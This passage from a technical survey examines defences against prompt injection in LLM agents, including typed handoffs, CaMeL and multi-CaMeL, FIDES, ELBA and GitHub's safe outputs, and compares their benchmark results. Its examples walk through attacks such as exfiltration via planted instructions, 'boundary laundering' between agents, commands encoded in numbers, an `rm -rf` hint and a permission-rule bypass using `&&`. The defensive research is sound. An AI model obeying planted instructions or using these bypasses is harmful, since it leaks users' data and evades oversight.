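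An opaque variable can also become an input to an action. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives an example in which the quarantined model finds an email address in untrusted text, and the privileged model sends a message to whatever address the variable holds. An attacker can't add an action to this plan but may be able to choose the recipient. A later system called CaMeL addresses this gap by tracking where each value came from.

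The pattern fails completely when the next action depends on what the text means. In a software-repair assistant, for example, the privileged model mustn't read bug reports from a public project, because anyone can file one. But without the report, it can't identify which of thousands of files to look at. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) tested a pair of models on 232 bugs and let nothing return from the quarantined model to the privileged one. The pair fixed none of the bugs, while an unprotected agent fixed 61.2%.

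### Letting four types of value through

Willison had allowed one exception, for when the quarantined model sorts a text into one of a fixed set of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of those categories and pass it on. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give a similar example, in which a separate model reads each file in a folder and answers yes or no to whether it is an invoice. Someone who writes a malicious file can only get it marked as an invoice, which they could also do by writing a fake invoice.

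Jacob and colleagues turned this exception into a general method, type-directed privilege separation, which they first published in 2025 and later revised. The quarantined model may return four types of value:

- integers
- floats, which are numbers with a fractional part
- booleans, which are true or false
- enums, which are choices from a list that the designer has checked in advance

It can combine these into records and arrays, and can still fill opaque variables. The privileged model never receives free text from it. Jacob and colleagues call each set of returned values a handoff and designed one for each of three agents.

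The first agent takes a shopping request, searches a simulated online shop with about 1.2 million products and buys one. Strangers write the reviews, so the quarantined model reads each review and returns two integers from 0 to 10, one for how strongly the review supports the product and one for how relevant it is. The privileged agent uses the median of each score. If five reviews of a kettle get scores of 9, 8, 9, 7 and 8, the median is 8, and it stays at 8 if a planted instruction changes the first score to 0. The agent also sees the number of reviews, because a hostile review sets the median when it is the only one.

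The second agent arranges meetings by email. The quarantined model passes the privileged model an array of suggested times, each chosen from a fixed list of slots, and an opaque variable that describes the meeting. The privileged model compares the times with the user's calendar and either proposes other times or books the meeting. A separate model, isolated from the quarantined one, writes the replies.

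The booked event includes the opaque description, which the other person may have written. Unless the program hides the descriptions of such events, the privileged model may read that text in the calendar the next time it arranges a meeting. The experiment arranged only one meeting for each pair of people, so it couldn't reveal this weakness in the design.

The third agent fixes bugs, and its handoff is the most elaborate. The quarantined model reads the report, explores the code and returns:

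- one of 52 categories of bug
- one of three sizes of repair
- an array of suspicious regions in the code, each with a file's index number, a first line, a last line and one of eight roles, such as "suspected to contain the bug"

A planner model, which never sees the report, uses this handoff to write three repair plans in plain English. A quarantined judge compares the plans with the report and returns only the number of the best one, so there is no need to limit how much text it reads. The privileged agent then repairs the code using the handoff and the chosen plan.

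### What the three experiments found

Utility in the table below is the share of tasks the agent completed when not under attack. A shopping task counted as completed if the agent earned full marks for its purchase in at least three of five trials. Attack success is the share of attacked runs in which the planted instruction worked. For shopping, it covers only products the agent would otherwise have chosen.

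| Agent | Model | Tasks | Utility without protection | Utility with typed handoff | Attack success without protection | Attack success with typed handoff |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | GPT-4o | 500 | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar | GPT-4o | 100 | 90% | 91% | 63% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 180 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The gains in the first two rows amount to three purchases and one meeting, so they are probably due to chance. The third row shows a real loss, with the protected agent fixing 81 bugs instead of 123, about a third fewer.

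The zeros follow from the design. The attacker in the calendar test asked for the user's whole calendar, and the quarantined model can't express that request as a list of meeting times. But each experiment used one fixed text written to hijack an ordinary agent. The shopping attack, for example, was a claim in capital letters that the product was a banned substance. None of the texts was designed to pass a command through the numbers, so the tests show that Jacob and colleagues connected the parts correctly but give little evidence about the limits of the types.

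Jacob and colleagues blame the loss on the bug reports, which describe real problems in ordinary language. This seems right. A shopper mainly needs to know how much other buyers liked a kettle, and a number from 0 to 10 conveys most of that. Similarly, a slot conveys a meeting time exactly. But a bug report often explains what the program should do. Suppose a report says that a calendar program should start the week on Saturday for users in Egypt. In the handoff, the model can point to lines 40 to 52 of a file and choose "incorrect default value", but it can't specify "Saturday". The designer can't list every behaviour that users might ask for.

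*Twin Agent* suggests that a few words would often be enough. The model that reads the report can send the acting model a hint of up to 100 characters at each step. The system fixed 62.5% of the 232 bugs, about as many as the unprotected agent. This result is only roughly comparable with the 45% above, because the two experiments used different selections of bugs. But the hints are free text, so Hu and colleagues had to add a filter for planted instructions, and they claim no formal guarantee.

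Attacks written specifically for this design led to the malicious action in 11 of the 232 runs (4.7%). When those 11 runs were repeated five times each, the attack never worked again, so luck plays a large part. But an attacker who can file many reports doesn't need it to work every time. The character limit also applies to each hint separately, so a run of 50 steps can bring in 5,000 characters.

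Even one short string can be dangerous. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a quarantined model could turn a stranger's documentation into a list of functions, with names limited to 30 characters. Willison (2025), in a blog post also called *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, doubts that this is safe and gives the example `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`. A model might take this 29-character name as advice to run `rm -rf`, which deletes a folder and everything in it.

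Labelled fields don't keep planted text out if they hold free text. *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw* (2026) tested a pair of agents in which the first passed summaries to the second in JSON, a common text format for structured data. Planted text leaked into the summaries 63.7% of the time. The paper argues that the format still made the text harder to act on, but concedes that the defence weakens if attackers learn to write instructions that survive inside the fields.

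### Choosing the type with each question

Jacob and colleagues needed a lot of testing to settle on the bug-fixing handoff, and a fixed handoff can't anticipate every question. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) lets the privileged agent choose the type each time it asks. The agent uses websites, where a shop's own buttons appear next to strangers' comments. The system replaces strangers' content with placeholders such as "user comment". The agent can then ask a quarantined model a question about one placeholder and specify the type of the answer. It can also write the options for an enum itself, because it hasn't read any hostile text.

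On 100 tasks across ten purpose-built websites, the masked agents did about as well as unprotected ones, and the median cost per task rose by between 5% and 84%. None of the instructions that Nikolić and colleagues planted in web pages hijacked the masked agents. But on GitLab, a real site for managing code, they found attacks that can make an agent act on the wrong item by giving it false answers of the right type. These attacks assume that the attacker fully controls the quarantined model's answers. The agents solved most of the GitLab tasks but couldn't handle questions that need answers in words, such as what new feature somebody is requesting. Letting the user approve text answers restored the lost performance. The protection then depends on the user reading each answer carefully, and Willison expects people to get used to clicking "OK".

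The method also depends on masking the right parts of the page. The tests mostly used labels made by hand. When a model inferred the labels from the page's structure, it missed none of the untrusted kinds of element on Reddit, about 7% on Booking.com and about 10% on GitLab. The agent would directly see any text planted in the missed elements.

### Whether a number can carry a command

An integer can contain an injected command if it is long enough. If 01 stands for a, 02 for b and so on up to 26 for z, the word "pay" becomes 160125. Any instruction can be written this way, and one of 100 letters needs only 200 digits. Jacob and colleagues argue that an integer can't contain an injected command because a command needs free text, but their definition of the type allows integers of any length.

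If a text editor receives 160125 as a line number, it looks for that line. A language model, trained on text that includes many codes, might recognise the number as a coded message. It would still have to do this, decode the message and obey it without any instruction in the handoff to do so. This is much harder to bring about than an ordinary prompt injection, but limits on numbers have almost no drawbacks, so there is little reason to leave the possibility open.

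An array can spell a word one element at a time. For example, regions that start at lines 16, 1 and 25 spell "pay" if each number stands for a letter of the alphabet. Jacob and colleagues recognise this risk and limit the length of arrays to "some small upper bound". But their calendar and bug-fixing schemas let the quarantined model choose the length, presumably up to that bound. The schemas also describe the file index and the line numbers only as integers. Of the three handoffs, only the shopping one gives its numbers a range.

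A program can set tighter limits for the bug-fixing handoff because it can count the files and lines itself:

- The file index must belong to an existing file.
- The first line must exist in that file, and the last line must exist and not come before the first.
- The array may hold at most five regions, in the order in which they appear in the code, with no repeats.

The last rule stops the quarantined model from using the order of the regions to spell anything. Floats need a minimum, a maximum and a fixed number of decimal places, or the digits after the decimal point could carry the text instead. The model will always have some choice of values, and a compromised model can hide a little information in that choice.

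Enums need limits too, because a long array of choices from a list of 26 letters can spell out any text. The options must also come from somebody the designer trusts. If a program builds the list from product names, the sellers have written the options. The bug-fixing agent is close to this case, because its program replaces each index number with the file's name before the privileged model reads the handoff. Jacob and colleagues treat the code repository as trusted, but strangers contribute files and comments to open-source projects. The privileged model may therefore read strangers' text in the repository even though it never sees the bug report.

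### Making the model keep to the types

A language model normally generates likely text, which may not be a valid handoff. To force it to produce one, Jacob and colleagues use "structured outputs", a feature that most model providers offer. This feature usually relies on constrained generation, which removes invalid options each time the model picks a token.

Suppose a model's whole vocabulary is `0`, `1`, `9`, `Buy`, `now` and a marker that ends the answer. The permitted answers are the whole numbers from 0 to 10. A hostile review has told the model to write "Buy now", so it gives `Buy` a probability of 90% at the first step. The program sets the probability of every token that can't begin a permitted answer to zero, then scales up the rest until they add up to 100%. Say the model then happens to pick `1`. The program repeats the process for the second token:

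| Token | First step, model's probability | First step, after removal | Second step, model's probability | Second step, after removal |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `0` | 1% | 11% | 12% | 75% |
| `1` | 3% | 33% | 2% | 0% |
| `9` | 5% | 56% | 1% | 0% |
| `Buy` | 90% | 0% | 60% | 0% |
| `now` | 1% | 0% | 21% | 0% |
| End marker | 0% | 0% | 4% | 25% |

After `1`, the answer can end there or continue to 10. If the model picks `0`, the only token left at the third step is the end marker, and the answer is 10. In symbols, let V be the set of tokens that can still lead to a permitted answer, and let p(t) be the model's probability for token t. The program uses

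q(t) = p(t) / Σ p(u), where the sum runs over all tokens u in V,

for every token in V, and zero for the others.

The program that works out V is a recogniser that checks the answer as the model writes it. The model in the example can't write "Buy now", however likely the review makes that answer. It wrote 10 only because the program had removed everything it was most likely to write, so the 10 doesn't mean that the review was favourable.

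The receiver should still check the finished answer. Constrained generation often runs on the provider's computers, where the receiver's owner can't inspect it, and a colleague might switch to a model that doesn't offer it. A provider's version may enforce only some of a schema's rules. It also can't apply rules that depend on the receiver's own data, such as whether a file has a line 52. If a length limit cuts the answer off, 10 can become 1, which is also valid, so the receiver should require an explicit sign that the answer is complete.

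When a check fails, many programs repeat the invalid value in the error message. If the quarantined model returns a planted instruction instead of a number and the controller passes the error on to the privileged model, the privileged model will also receive the instruction. A fixed message such as "invalid answer" avoids this.

### Models that can only submit requests

The same restriction works for actions. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe the *action-selector* pattern, in which a model reads a request and picks one or more actions from a fixed list. Their example is a customer-service chatbot that can fetch a link to the customer's last order, or direct the customer to the password settings page or the payment settings page. The help desk with three answers works this way too. An action, such as a prepared database query, can have gaps for the model to fill in, and each gap then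 needs its own type.

The results of an action never go back to the model, so text in the results can't influence what it does next. This makes the pattern simple and very safe, but the model can't look up an order and then decide what to do about it. A hostile message can still make the model pick the wrong action, as at the help desk.

The code-sharing website GitHub uses a broader version in its Agentic Workflows, which let an AI agent do routine work on a project, such as sorting bug reports. According to GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026), the designers assume that the agent will try to write things it shouldn't and misuse legitimate channels. The agent can read the project but can't change it. It can only submit requests, called "safe outputs", which the system holds until the agent has finished.

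The project's owner lists the permitted kinds of request, for example creating up to three issues (GitHub's term for bug reports and other tasks). GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026) requires the system to offer the agent tools only for those kinds of request. The system checks the structure of each request and writes it to a file. A separate job, which does have permission to change the project, then reads the file and must finish all its checks on a request before carrying it out.

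| Part of the request | Who decides | What the system does |
|---|---|---|
| Kind of operation | The agent, from the owner's list | Offers no tool for anything else |
| Number of requests | The agent, up to the owner's maximum | Rejects the whole batch if there are too many |
| Project to change | The owner | Allows only the current project unless the owner lists others |
| Existing issue to change | The owner or the event that started the run | Ignores the agent's choice unless the owner allows any issue |
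| Title and text | The agent | Removes suspicious content |

Suppose a stranger files an issue that tells the agent to delete the project and post 500 advertisements. The agent has no tool for deleting projects, and the system would reject a batch of 500. But the agent could still post three advertisements.

The last row of the table, GitHub's *Safe Outputs*, is a filter. According to its reference page, an issue can contain up to 65,000 characters of text. The system removes links to unapproved websites and looks for passwords and keys, but GitHub rates its detection of unknown keys as only moderately effective, because new formats can evade it. GitHub also acknowledges that an agent can write plausible but inappropriate text within the limits. The specification describes what the system must do but doesn't measure how well it withstands attacks.

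The protection also depends on which requests the owner enables. An agent that can only add existing labels can do little harm, but one that can propose code changes can propose a backdoor. The usual defence is for a person to review each change. The owner can also fix which branch (version of the code) a change goes to. GitHub's *Safe Outputs (Pull Requests)* explains that the system then ignores any other branch the agent asks for, unless the owner has approved it. But GitHub also offers an experimental request that merges a change automatically once it passes the project's rules. If those rules don't require human review, the change may take effect without anyone reading it.

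Another permitted request starts a new session with a coding agent. A hijacked agent could use it to pass planted text to an agent with different powers, and an ordinary issue can also pass on such text if another agent reads it later. GitHub therefore also restricts what its agents read. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes a system that hides items from an agent based on the author's relationship to the project and who has vetted them. An owner who hides every stranger's issue blocks this route of attack, but the agent can no longer sort the bug reports that strangers file.

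## Separating instructions from data between planners, tools and agents

A designer can let strangers' text pass through an agent as data instead of hiding it from the agent, as long as the text never reaches the model that chooses the actions. The Dual LLM pattern does this with opaque variables, but an attacker can still influence what those variables hold. CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, adds a record of where each value came from and who may read it.

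### How CaMeL handles a request

Suppose the shop's manager asks an assistant to find the courier's email address in the warehouse chat and send him today's parcel list. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how CaMeL works, and for this request the steps would be:

1. The privileged model reads the manager's request and a description of the tools, then writes a short program in a restricted version of Python. It hasn't seen the chat or the parcel list.
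2. An ordinary program, the interpreter, runs this code and calls the tools.
3. When the code needs a fact from the chat, the interpreter passes the chat to a quarantined model, which returns a value of the requested type.
4. The interpreter stores each result with a label that lists its sources and its permitted readers. It also tracks which earlier values each new value depends on.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a function that receives the tool's name, the arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny".

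The privileged model's program might look like this:

```
chat = read_channel("warehouse")
address = ask_quarantined("Find the courier's email address", chat, EmailAddress)
parcels = read_file("parcels-today")
send_email(to=address, body=parcels)
```

Now someone posts a chat message telling the assistant to email the customer database to a thief. The quarantined model may try to follow the instruction, but it can only return a value for `address`. The program is already written, and no line in it opens the customer database. The attack is inexpressible, as it would be in any restricted channel, because the permitted set contains only the possible runs of these four lines. If the program had an "if" in it, planted text might decide which branch runs, but it couldn't add a new one.

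A cleverer attacker posts that the courier's email address has changed, and gives the thief's. The quarantined model returns this valid address, and the program is about to email the thief the parcel list, which includes customers' home addresses. The program has no check that prevents this, so the policy has to. Suppose the list's label names the shop's staff and the real courier as its permitted readers. The policy can require every recipient to be a permitted reader (T ⊆ R, where T is the set of recipients and R is the set of permitted readers). *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) calls this rule "permitted flow". The thief isn't in R, so the interpreter blocks the email.

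The policy checks a finished request, after the attacker has chosen the address but before the email is sent. Like the £100 limit on refunds, it only compares values, so it's more dependable than a filter that reads prose. But someone has to write the policy and label the data correctly. If the shop had marked the parcel list as public, the attacker would have received it.

These labels are the "capabilities" in CaMeL's full name, Capabilities for Machine Learning. A label describes a value but doesn't give anyone the right to use it, so it isn't a capability in Hardy's sense.

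### Checking the program before it runs

CaMeL's interpreter checks a tool call only when the program reaches it, which can waste work. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of an agent that helps a company's security team by analysing an alert and then disconnecting the affected computer from the network. Disconnecting it requires another team's approval. If the program has no step for requesting approval, CaMeL detects the omission only at the last line, after the whole analysis has run.

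Their extension, CaMeLoT, checks the program before any tool runs. It turns the program into a finite set of states and gives them to a model checker, which explores every possible path through them. The rules are in a logic that can describe whole paths. One of them is

AG(send_money → ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted)).

AG means "in every state on every path". If the program sends money, neither the recipient nor the amount may come from untrusted data. A similar rule could reject the courier program immediately, because its text shows that the address comes from the quarantined model. Other rules require something to happen eventually, such as the program closing every ticket it opens. CaMeL's own policies can't naturally express such requirements, because they check one call at a time.

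When a program breaks a rule, the model checker produces the path that breaks it, and the privileged model gets a description of that path and tries again. No tool has run yet, so the description can't contain text from a stranger's message. The checker assumes that a loop can stop after any number of rounds, so it rejects some safe programs. Rules that depend on actual values, such as whether a particular address is on the list of readers, can only be checked when the program runs.

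### What the policies cost

AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark for prompt injection, has 97 harmless tasks in simulated offices, banks, travel agencies and Slack workspaces. It also has 35 attack goals, which it plants as instructions in tool results. According to Peters-Gill and colleagues, CaMeL was much more secure in earlier AgentDojo tests than lighter defences, such as repeating the user's request after the untrusted text, and the loss of usefulness was fairly modest.

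Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, reran CaMeL on the 21 Slack tasks with newer models and found a much larger loss once the policies were on:

| Model | Tasks completed without policies | Tasks completed with policies |
|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 15 | 5 |
| Opus 4.8 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT 5.4 | 17 | 5 |
| Sonnet 5 | 13 | 4 |

On average, the policies cut the share of completed tasks from 73% to 24%. Writing the program in advance can't have lowered it nearly as much on these tasks, because CaMeL without policies failed only 27% of them. Many Slack tasks involve passing on text from web pages or other people, which is probably why the policies blocked so many of them. The sample is small, and Zhou and colleagues were comparing CaMeL with their own system.

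Every attack in this comparison failed, with or without policies, so it doesn't show how much security the policies add.

According to *ToolFence* (2026), CaMeL is also significantly slower than defences based on prompts or filters, because each task can involve writing a program, rewriting it after errors and making extra calls to the quarantined model.

### When one agent instructs another

Large jobs are often split among several agents. An orchestrator agent receives the user's request and calls specialist agents as if they were tools. Each specialist treats the orchestrator as its user. Peters-Gill and colleagues built such a system from three agents, each protected by CaMeL. GPT-5.2 served as both the privileged and the quarantined model. One specialist could query a database of job applicants, and the other could send emails and Slack messages.

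The user asked the orchestrator to send Julie a summary of the applicants on Slack. The database also contained a planted instruction to send the applicants' details to an outside email address. The attack went as follows:

1. The orchestrator's privileged model wrote a program that would fetch the applicants' details, have them summarised and ask the messaging agent to send the summary to Julie.
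2. The database agent ran its query and returned the result, including the planted instruction. Neither agent's privileged model saw it.
3. The orchestrator's quarantined model wrote the summary, and the planted instruction came through with it.
4. The orchestrator's program pasted the summary into a sentence that began by asking the messaging agent to send it to Julie.
5. The messaging agent took the whole sentence as its user's request. Its privileged model read the planted instruction and wrote a program with an extra line, which emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

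The attack did not change the orchestrator's program or the database agent's. Each of the three agents behaved as CaMeL guarantees, yet the system as a whole followed the attacker's instruction. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering", because untrusted text becomes trusted when it crosses from one agent to another. Pasting the summary into an instruction is the same mistake as the one on the login page.

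The experiment ran without policies, but a policy in the messaging agent might not have helped, because that agent's model copied the summary into its own program as a fixed string, which normally counts as trusted. A policy that blocked all email to outside addresses would have worked, but it would also have blocked legitimate email.

Protecting each agent separately stops attacks that depend on hijacking the agent that first receives the planted text. In one such attack, text planted in a public database makes a database agent query a private database. Peters-Gill and colleagues tried this five times against agents protected by CaMeL, and it failed each time. Five attempts are few, but CaMeL's design explains the result. The agent's program is written before the planted text is read, so the text can't add a query to it.

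### Why the weakness is general

Peters-Gill and colleagues also study systems in which agents form a tree and each parent calls its children as tools. They prove that if such a system has at least two agents and any of its tools returns untrusted data, some user request will let untrusted data shape an agent's plan, even if every agent is secure on its own.

The proof relies on an "expressivity assumption" that the agents are reasonably flexible. A user can ask any agent to use any one of its tools and report the result. A user can also ask it to use two tools in sequence, or the same tool twice, with the second input depending on the first result. For an agent, calling a child counts as using a tool.

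If an agent has a tool that returns untrusted data, a stranger's text can end up in an agent's instructions. If the agent has a child, someone can ask the agent to use the tool and then give the child an instruction based on the result, as the orchestrator did with the summary. If it has no child, it must have a parent, and someone can ask the parent to call the agent, then call it again with an instruction based on its first answer.

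Most useful agents meet this assumption, because "look this up and act on it" is a very common request. But the claim is only that a vulnerable request exists. It doesn't cover how often users make one or how often an attack on it would succeed. It also assumes that parents can write instructions based on whatever comes back. If a parent could only choose from ten prepared instructions, a stranger might influence the choice but couldn't add a new one.

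### Two arguments instead of one

The repair, multi-CaMeL, splits each call between agents into two arguments. In the applicant example, the orchestrator's call would become:

```
messaging_agent(
    message="Send the summary to Julie on Slack",
    variables={"summary": summary}
)
```

The messaging agent's privileged model reads only the message. It writes a program that, when run, fetches the summary by name and passes it to Slack. If the summary contains a planted instruction, Julie will see strange text in Slack, but the agent won't act on it. This works like the prepared statement, with the message as the command and the variables as the values that fill its gaps.

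The orchestrator's model is instructed to put anything it got from a tool into the variables, but it might not do so, so the interpreter enforces the rule by ensuring that no message depends on a tool's output. The variables keep their labels when they are passed on, so a policy in the messaging agent can still check who may read the summary. The variables' names need the same care as the message, because the receiving model needs them to use the variables.

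The guarantee depends on the interpreter tracking dependencies correctly, and research on the LLMbda calculus, a formal model of agents, found that CaMeL's interpreter misses some dependencies that pass through a condition. The proof also covers only trees, where each agent has one parent. When agents share a message queue or remember earlier conversations, old untrusted text could reappear as an instruction through more paths.

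### How well the repair worked

To test the repair, Peters-Gill and colleagues built MultiAgentDojo by dividing AgentDojo's tools among specialist agents under an orchestrator. They ran 949 attacked tasks for each of five models in each setting. Averaged over the models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without protection, 0.2% with CaMeL applied to each agent separately and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL.

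Two older models account for most of the first figure. Attacks on the unprotected agents succeeded 36.1% of the time with GPT-4.1 and 24.6% with Gemini 2.5 Pro, but no more than 2.1% with any other model. The 0.2% corresponds to about nine successful attacks out of 4,745, too few to measure the benefit of the repair precisely. But all of these attacks passed from one agent to another inside an instruction, as the theory predicts, and multi-CaMeL blocks that route.

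None of the benchmark's attacks succeeded against GPT-5.5 (0.0%), even with no added protection. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against concluding that the model is immune, because the attacks may be too weak. In a large public competition, attackers who could adapt had some success against every leading model tested. Zhou and colleagues also report that GPT-Red, OpenAI's own automated attack system, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences.

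Multi-CaMeL's 0.0% also has a limit. Peters-Gill and colleagues left the policies off in all their tests, so the systems they tested would have sent the parcel list to the false courier.

#### The cost of planning before seeing the data

They measured usefulness on AssetOpsBench, where an orchestrator and four specialists answer questions about industrial equipment, such as which of a chiller's sensors might reveal an overheating compressor. They removed 29 tasks that nobody could complete because the data didn't exist, which left 112. The table gives the share of tasks completed:

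| Model | No protection | CaMeL on each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% | 67.0% | 67.9% |
| GPT-5.5 | 87.5% | 82.1% | 79.5% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2% | 64.3% | 48.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% | 55.4% | 50.9% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 64.3% | 20.5% | 26.8% |

Running CaMeL on each agent lowered scores by 21.6 percentage points on average, and multi-CaMeL lowered them by another 3.2. The policies were off, so almost all of this loss comes from writing the program first. Stronger models generally lost less, but Fable 5 lost 20.5 points and GPT-5.5 only 8, though they scored about the same without protection. The losses were larger on MultiAgentDojo, where multi-CaMeL lowered GPT-5.5's score from 86.6% to 66.0% and GPT-4.1's from 78.4% to 24.7%.

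Most failures happened because the agent committed to a plan too early. When a lookup shows that another step is needed, an ordinary agent can take that step, but a CaMeL agent can do so only if the privileged model included it in the original plan. In other cases, a specialist couldn't find data for the requested dates and returned data for nearby ones. The orchestrator's program didn't check for this, so it continued with the wrong data.

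A capable model can anticipate some of these problems. In one run, Fable 5 wrote a program that would send a specialist a simpler question if the first one failed. The model also has to know the format of each tool's output before seeing any, so Peters-Gill and colleagues added full format descriptions to both benchmarks.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) calls a task data independent if a single sequence of tool calls and a final answer would solve it whatever the tools return. This definition helps to predict which tasks will suffer. Sending today's parcel list to a known address is data independent, because the agent takes the same steps whatever is on the list. Completing every job on someone's to-do list isn't, because the tools the agent needs depend on what the jobs are. CaMeL can handle some tasks that aren't data independent by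 writing a branch for each possibility, but only if the privileged model can predict the possibilities.

#### Securing the messages with filters instead

In *Beyond Single-Model Injection*, Paul and Nandy (2026) let agents exchange free text but signed each message, used a classifier to look for planted instructions, limited each agent's access to tools and watched for unusual patterns of communication. Together, these measures cut the success rate of attacks on a six-agent system from 31.2% to 4.2%. The exact number is doubtful because the models dated from 2024 and the figures for separate types of attack imply an overall rate nearer 3.2%.

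The classifier wrongly flagged 2.3% of harmless content. Limiting each agent's tools stopped every attempt to use one outside the agent's role, because the access rules don't depend on a message's content. Signing messages reduced attacks between agents from 31% to 2.8%, but a signature proves only which agent sent a message. In the applicant example, the orchestrator would have put a genuine signature on a message containing the attacker's instruction.

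### Letting the agent plan as it goes

Several other systems keep untrusted text out of the instructions but let the agent choose its next action after each result. This avoids some of CaMeL's failures, but more of the security depends on checks made when the agent acts.

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, labels everything the agent reads with how far it can be trusted and who may see it. When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result keeps the restrictions of both. If Ada and Ben may read one document and Ben and Cara another, only Ben may read a summary of both. Anything made partly from untrusted data is untrusted. The same rule applies to the text the planning model reads, so one stranger's email would make the whole conversation untrusted, and the policy would then block important actions.

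To prevent this, FIDES hides a result in a variable if reading it would change the conversation's label. The planner can read everything else directly. If it needs a fact from a hidden text, it can query a quarantined model for an answer in a fixed format.

With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo. Costa and colleagues report that without policy checks, every planner they tested, including FIDES, allowed practical attacks. With the checks on, FIDES completed 8% more tasks on average than a basic planner when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. The checks reduce the basic planner's task completion more because it reads everything, so its conversation soon becomes untrusted.

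#### Asking the user

*Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (Kim, Choi and Lee, 2025) describes a system in which the user decides whether to allow risky uses of untrusted data. A trusted agent sees identifiers such as `#DATA0` in place of untrusted text. It can pass an identifier to a tool, or ask a second agent with few permissions to extract something from the text behind it. Before untrusted data goes into an important action or the final answer, the system shows the user the data and its source and asks for approval. The trusted agent can also ask to read a text, such as an installation guide, as instructions, which also requires the user's approval.

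Kim and colleagues report that no attacks succeeded, but they count an attack as stopped once the user gets an alert, even though the user might still approve it. With GPT-4o, the system raised about 1.5 alerts per AgentDojo task, compared with 4.1 for a system that asks before every tool call. That is an improvement, but someone who gives an agent dozens of tasks a day would still get a lot of alerts.

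They also claim that the system has no false alarms. This is true only because they define any use of untrusted data in an important action as unsafe. Someone who asks for an emailed news summary will get an alert even if the news is harmless. The system took 63% longer than an unprotected agent on AgentDojo and used 91% more tokens. About three quarters of the additional failures happened because the 2024 models misused the identifiers or asked the second agent poor questions, so newer models might do better.

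#### Writing the policy as a type

ELBA, a system by Zhou and colleagues, uses the compiler to enforce policies, as Google did with its types for safe HTML. The agent writes programs in Haskell, where a program's type states both what kind of value it returns and what it can do to the outside world. If the developer asks for a program of type `Int`, the program can calculate a whole number but can't open a file or send anything. If the agent writes one that tries to, the compiler rejects it before it runs.

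In one ELBA example, an agent compiles bibliographies and may use only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The developer defines a type for trusted entries, and the only way to get a value of that type is to fetch it from DBLP. The command that writes to the bibliography accepts only values of that type, so the agent can't invent a reference. In a test, an ordinary agent with web search made up details in 19 of 1,002 citations, while the ELBA agent made up none in 925. ELBA guarantees that the citations came from the database, but not that they are relevant.

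Unlike CaMeL, ELBA lets an agent read a result and then write another program. It does this by calling another agent, whose program must satisfy the same type or a stricter one. For rules about who may read what, ELBA uses an existing Haskell library that checks labels while the program runs, so it still enforces those rules by checking finished requests. With policies on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks, compared with CaMeL's 4 to 6, but took about three times as long.

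Since ordinary attacks no longer worked on these models, Zhou and colleagues made the test harder by changing the system so that any agent that received a planted instruction would carry it out as its own task. Up to 42% of attacks then succeeded without policies, depending on the model, but all 735 failed on each of the four models when policies were on. This is better evidence than a benchmark on which the model might have ignored the attack, because it assumes that the attacker has already compromised the model. Under these conditions, the agents completed only 40% to 48% of their tasks with policies, compared with 67% to 76% without them.

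### What products use

All these results come from benchmarks. CaMeL, multi-CaMeL, FIDES, ELBA and Kim and colleagues' system have public code, so other people can test them, but public code isn't evidence that companies rely on them.

Zhou and colleagues describe coarser protections in products. Production systems commonly run agents in sandboxes that limit which files and networks they can reach. Google announced in December 2025 that Chrome would restrict which websites its agents can read or change. These controls limit where an agent can act, but they don't track where each value came from. If the courier's chat and the company's email are both permitted, a sandbox won't detect the thief's address. GitHub's safe outputs are closer to a restricted channel.

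Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, combines a sandbox with rules that match each command against text patterns or prompt the user for approval. Zhou and colleagues cite a user's report from March 2026 that these rules checked only the first part of a command joined with `&&`, so a forbidden command could follow a permitted one. They also point out that an agent can get around a ban on reading a file by writing a line of Python that opens it.

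## Harm done with permitted messages

When a forbidden command gets past a rule because it comes after `&&`, enforcement has failed. The shop's refund service could enforce its 41 messages without any such failure and still lose money, because a request for a full refund for a damaged lamp is valid even if the lamp is intact. The format limits what the assistant can request, but an attacker can still try to make it send a harmful request that the format permits.

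### False values

This kind of attack doesn't need a planted instruction. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives the example of an agent that fetches an invoice from a company called Acme on Monday and pays it on Tuesday. If an attacker has put his own account number on the invoice, the agent follows its user's plan exactly and pays the attacker. Checking the type won't help, because the false account number has the same format as the real one.

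The bug-fixing agent with the typed handoff has a similar weakness. Suppose a stranger files a bug report saying that a program locks people out after five wrong passwords. The quarantined model could point to the lines that set the limit and choose the category for a wrong default value. The privileged model might then raise the limit, which makes passwords easier to guess. Jacob and colleagues leave misleading reports out of their threat model and list them among the method's limitations. Running the program wouldn't expose the report as misleading, because the program does lock people out, and somebody has to know that the lockout is intended.

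SPA, the system that Girrens and Wang built, deals with false values by tracking how far each value can be trusted. Its planner writes a complete plan before any tool runs, as in CaMeL, and a checker then works through the plan. In a simple version with two levels, the user's own words have trust 1 and a stranger's invoice has trust 0. A value made from several sources gets the lowest trust among them:

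trust(v) = min(trust(s₁), …, trust(sₙ)).

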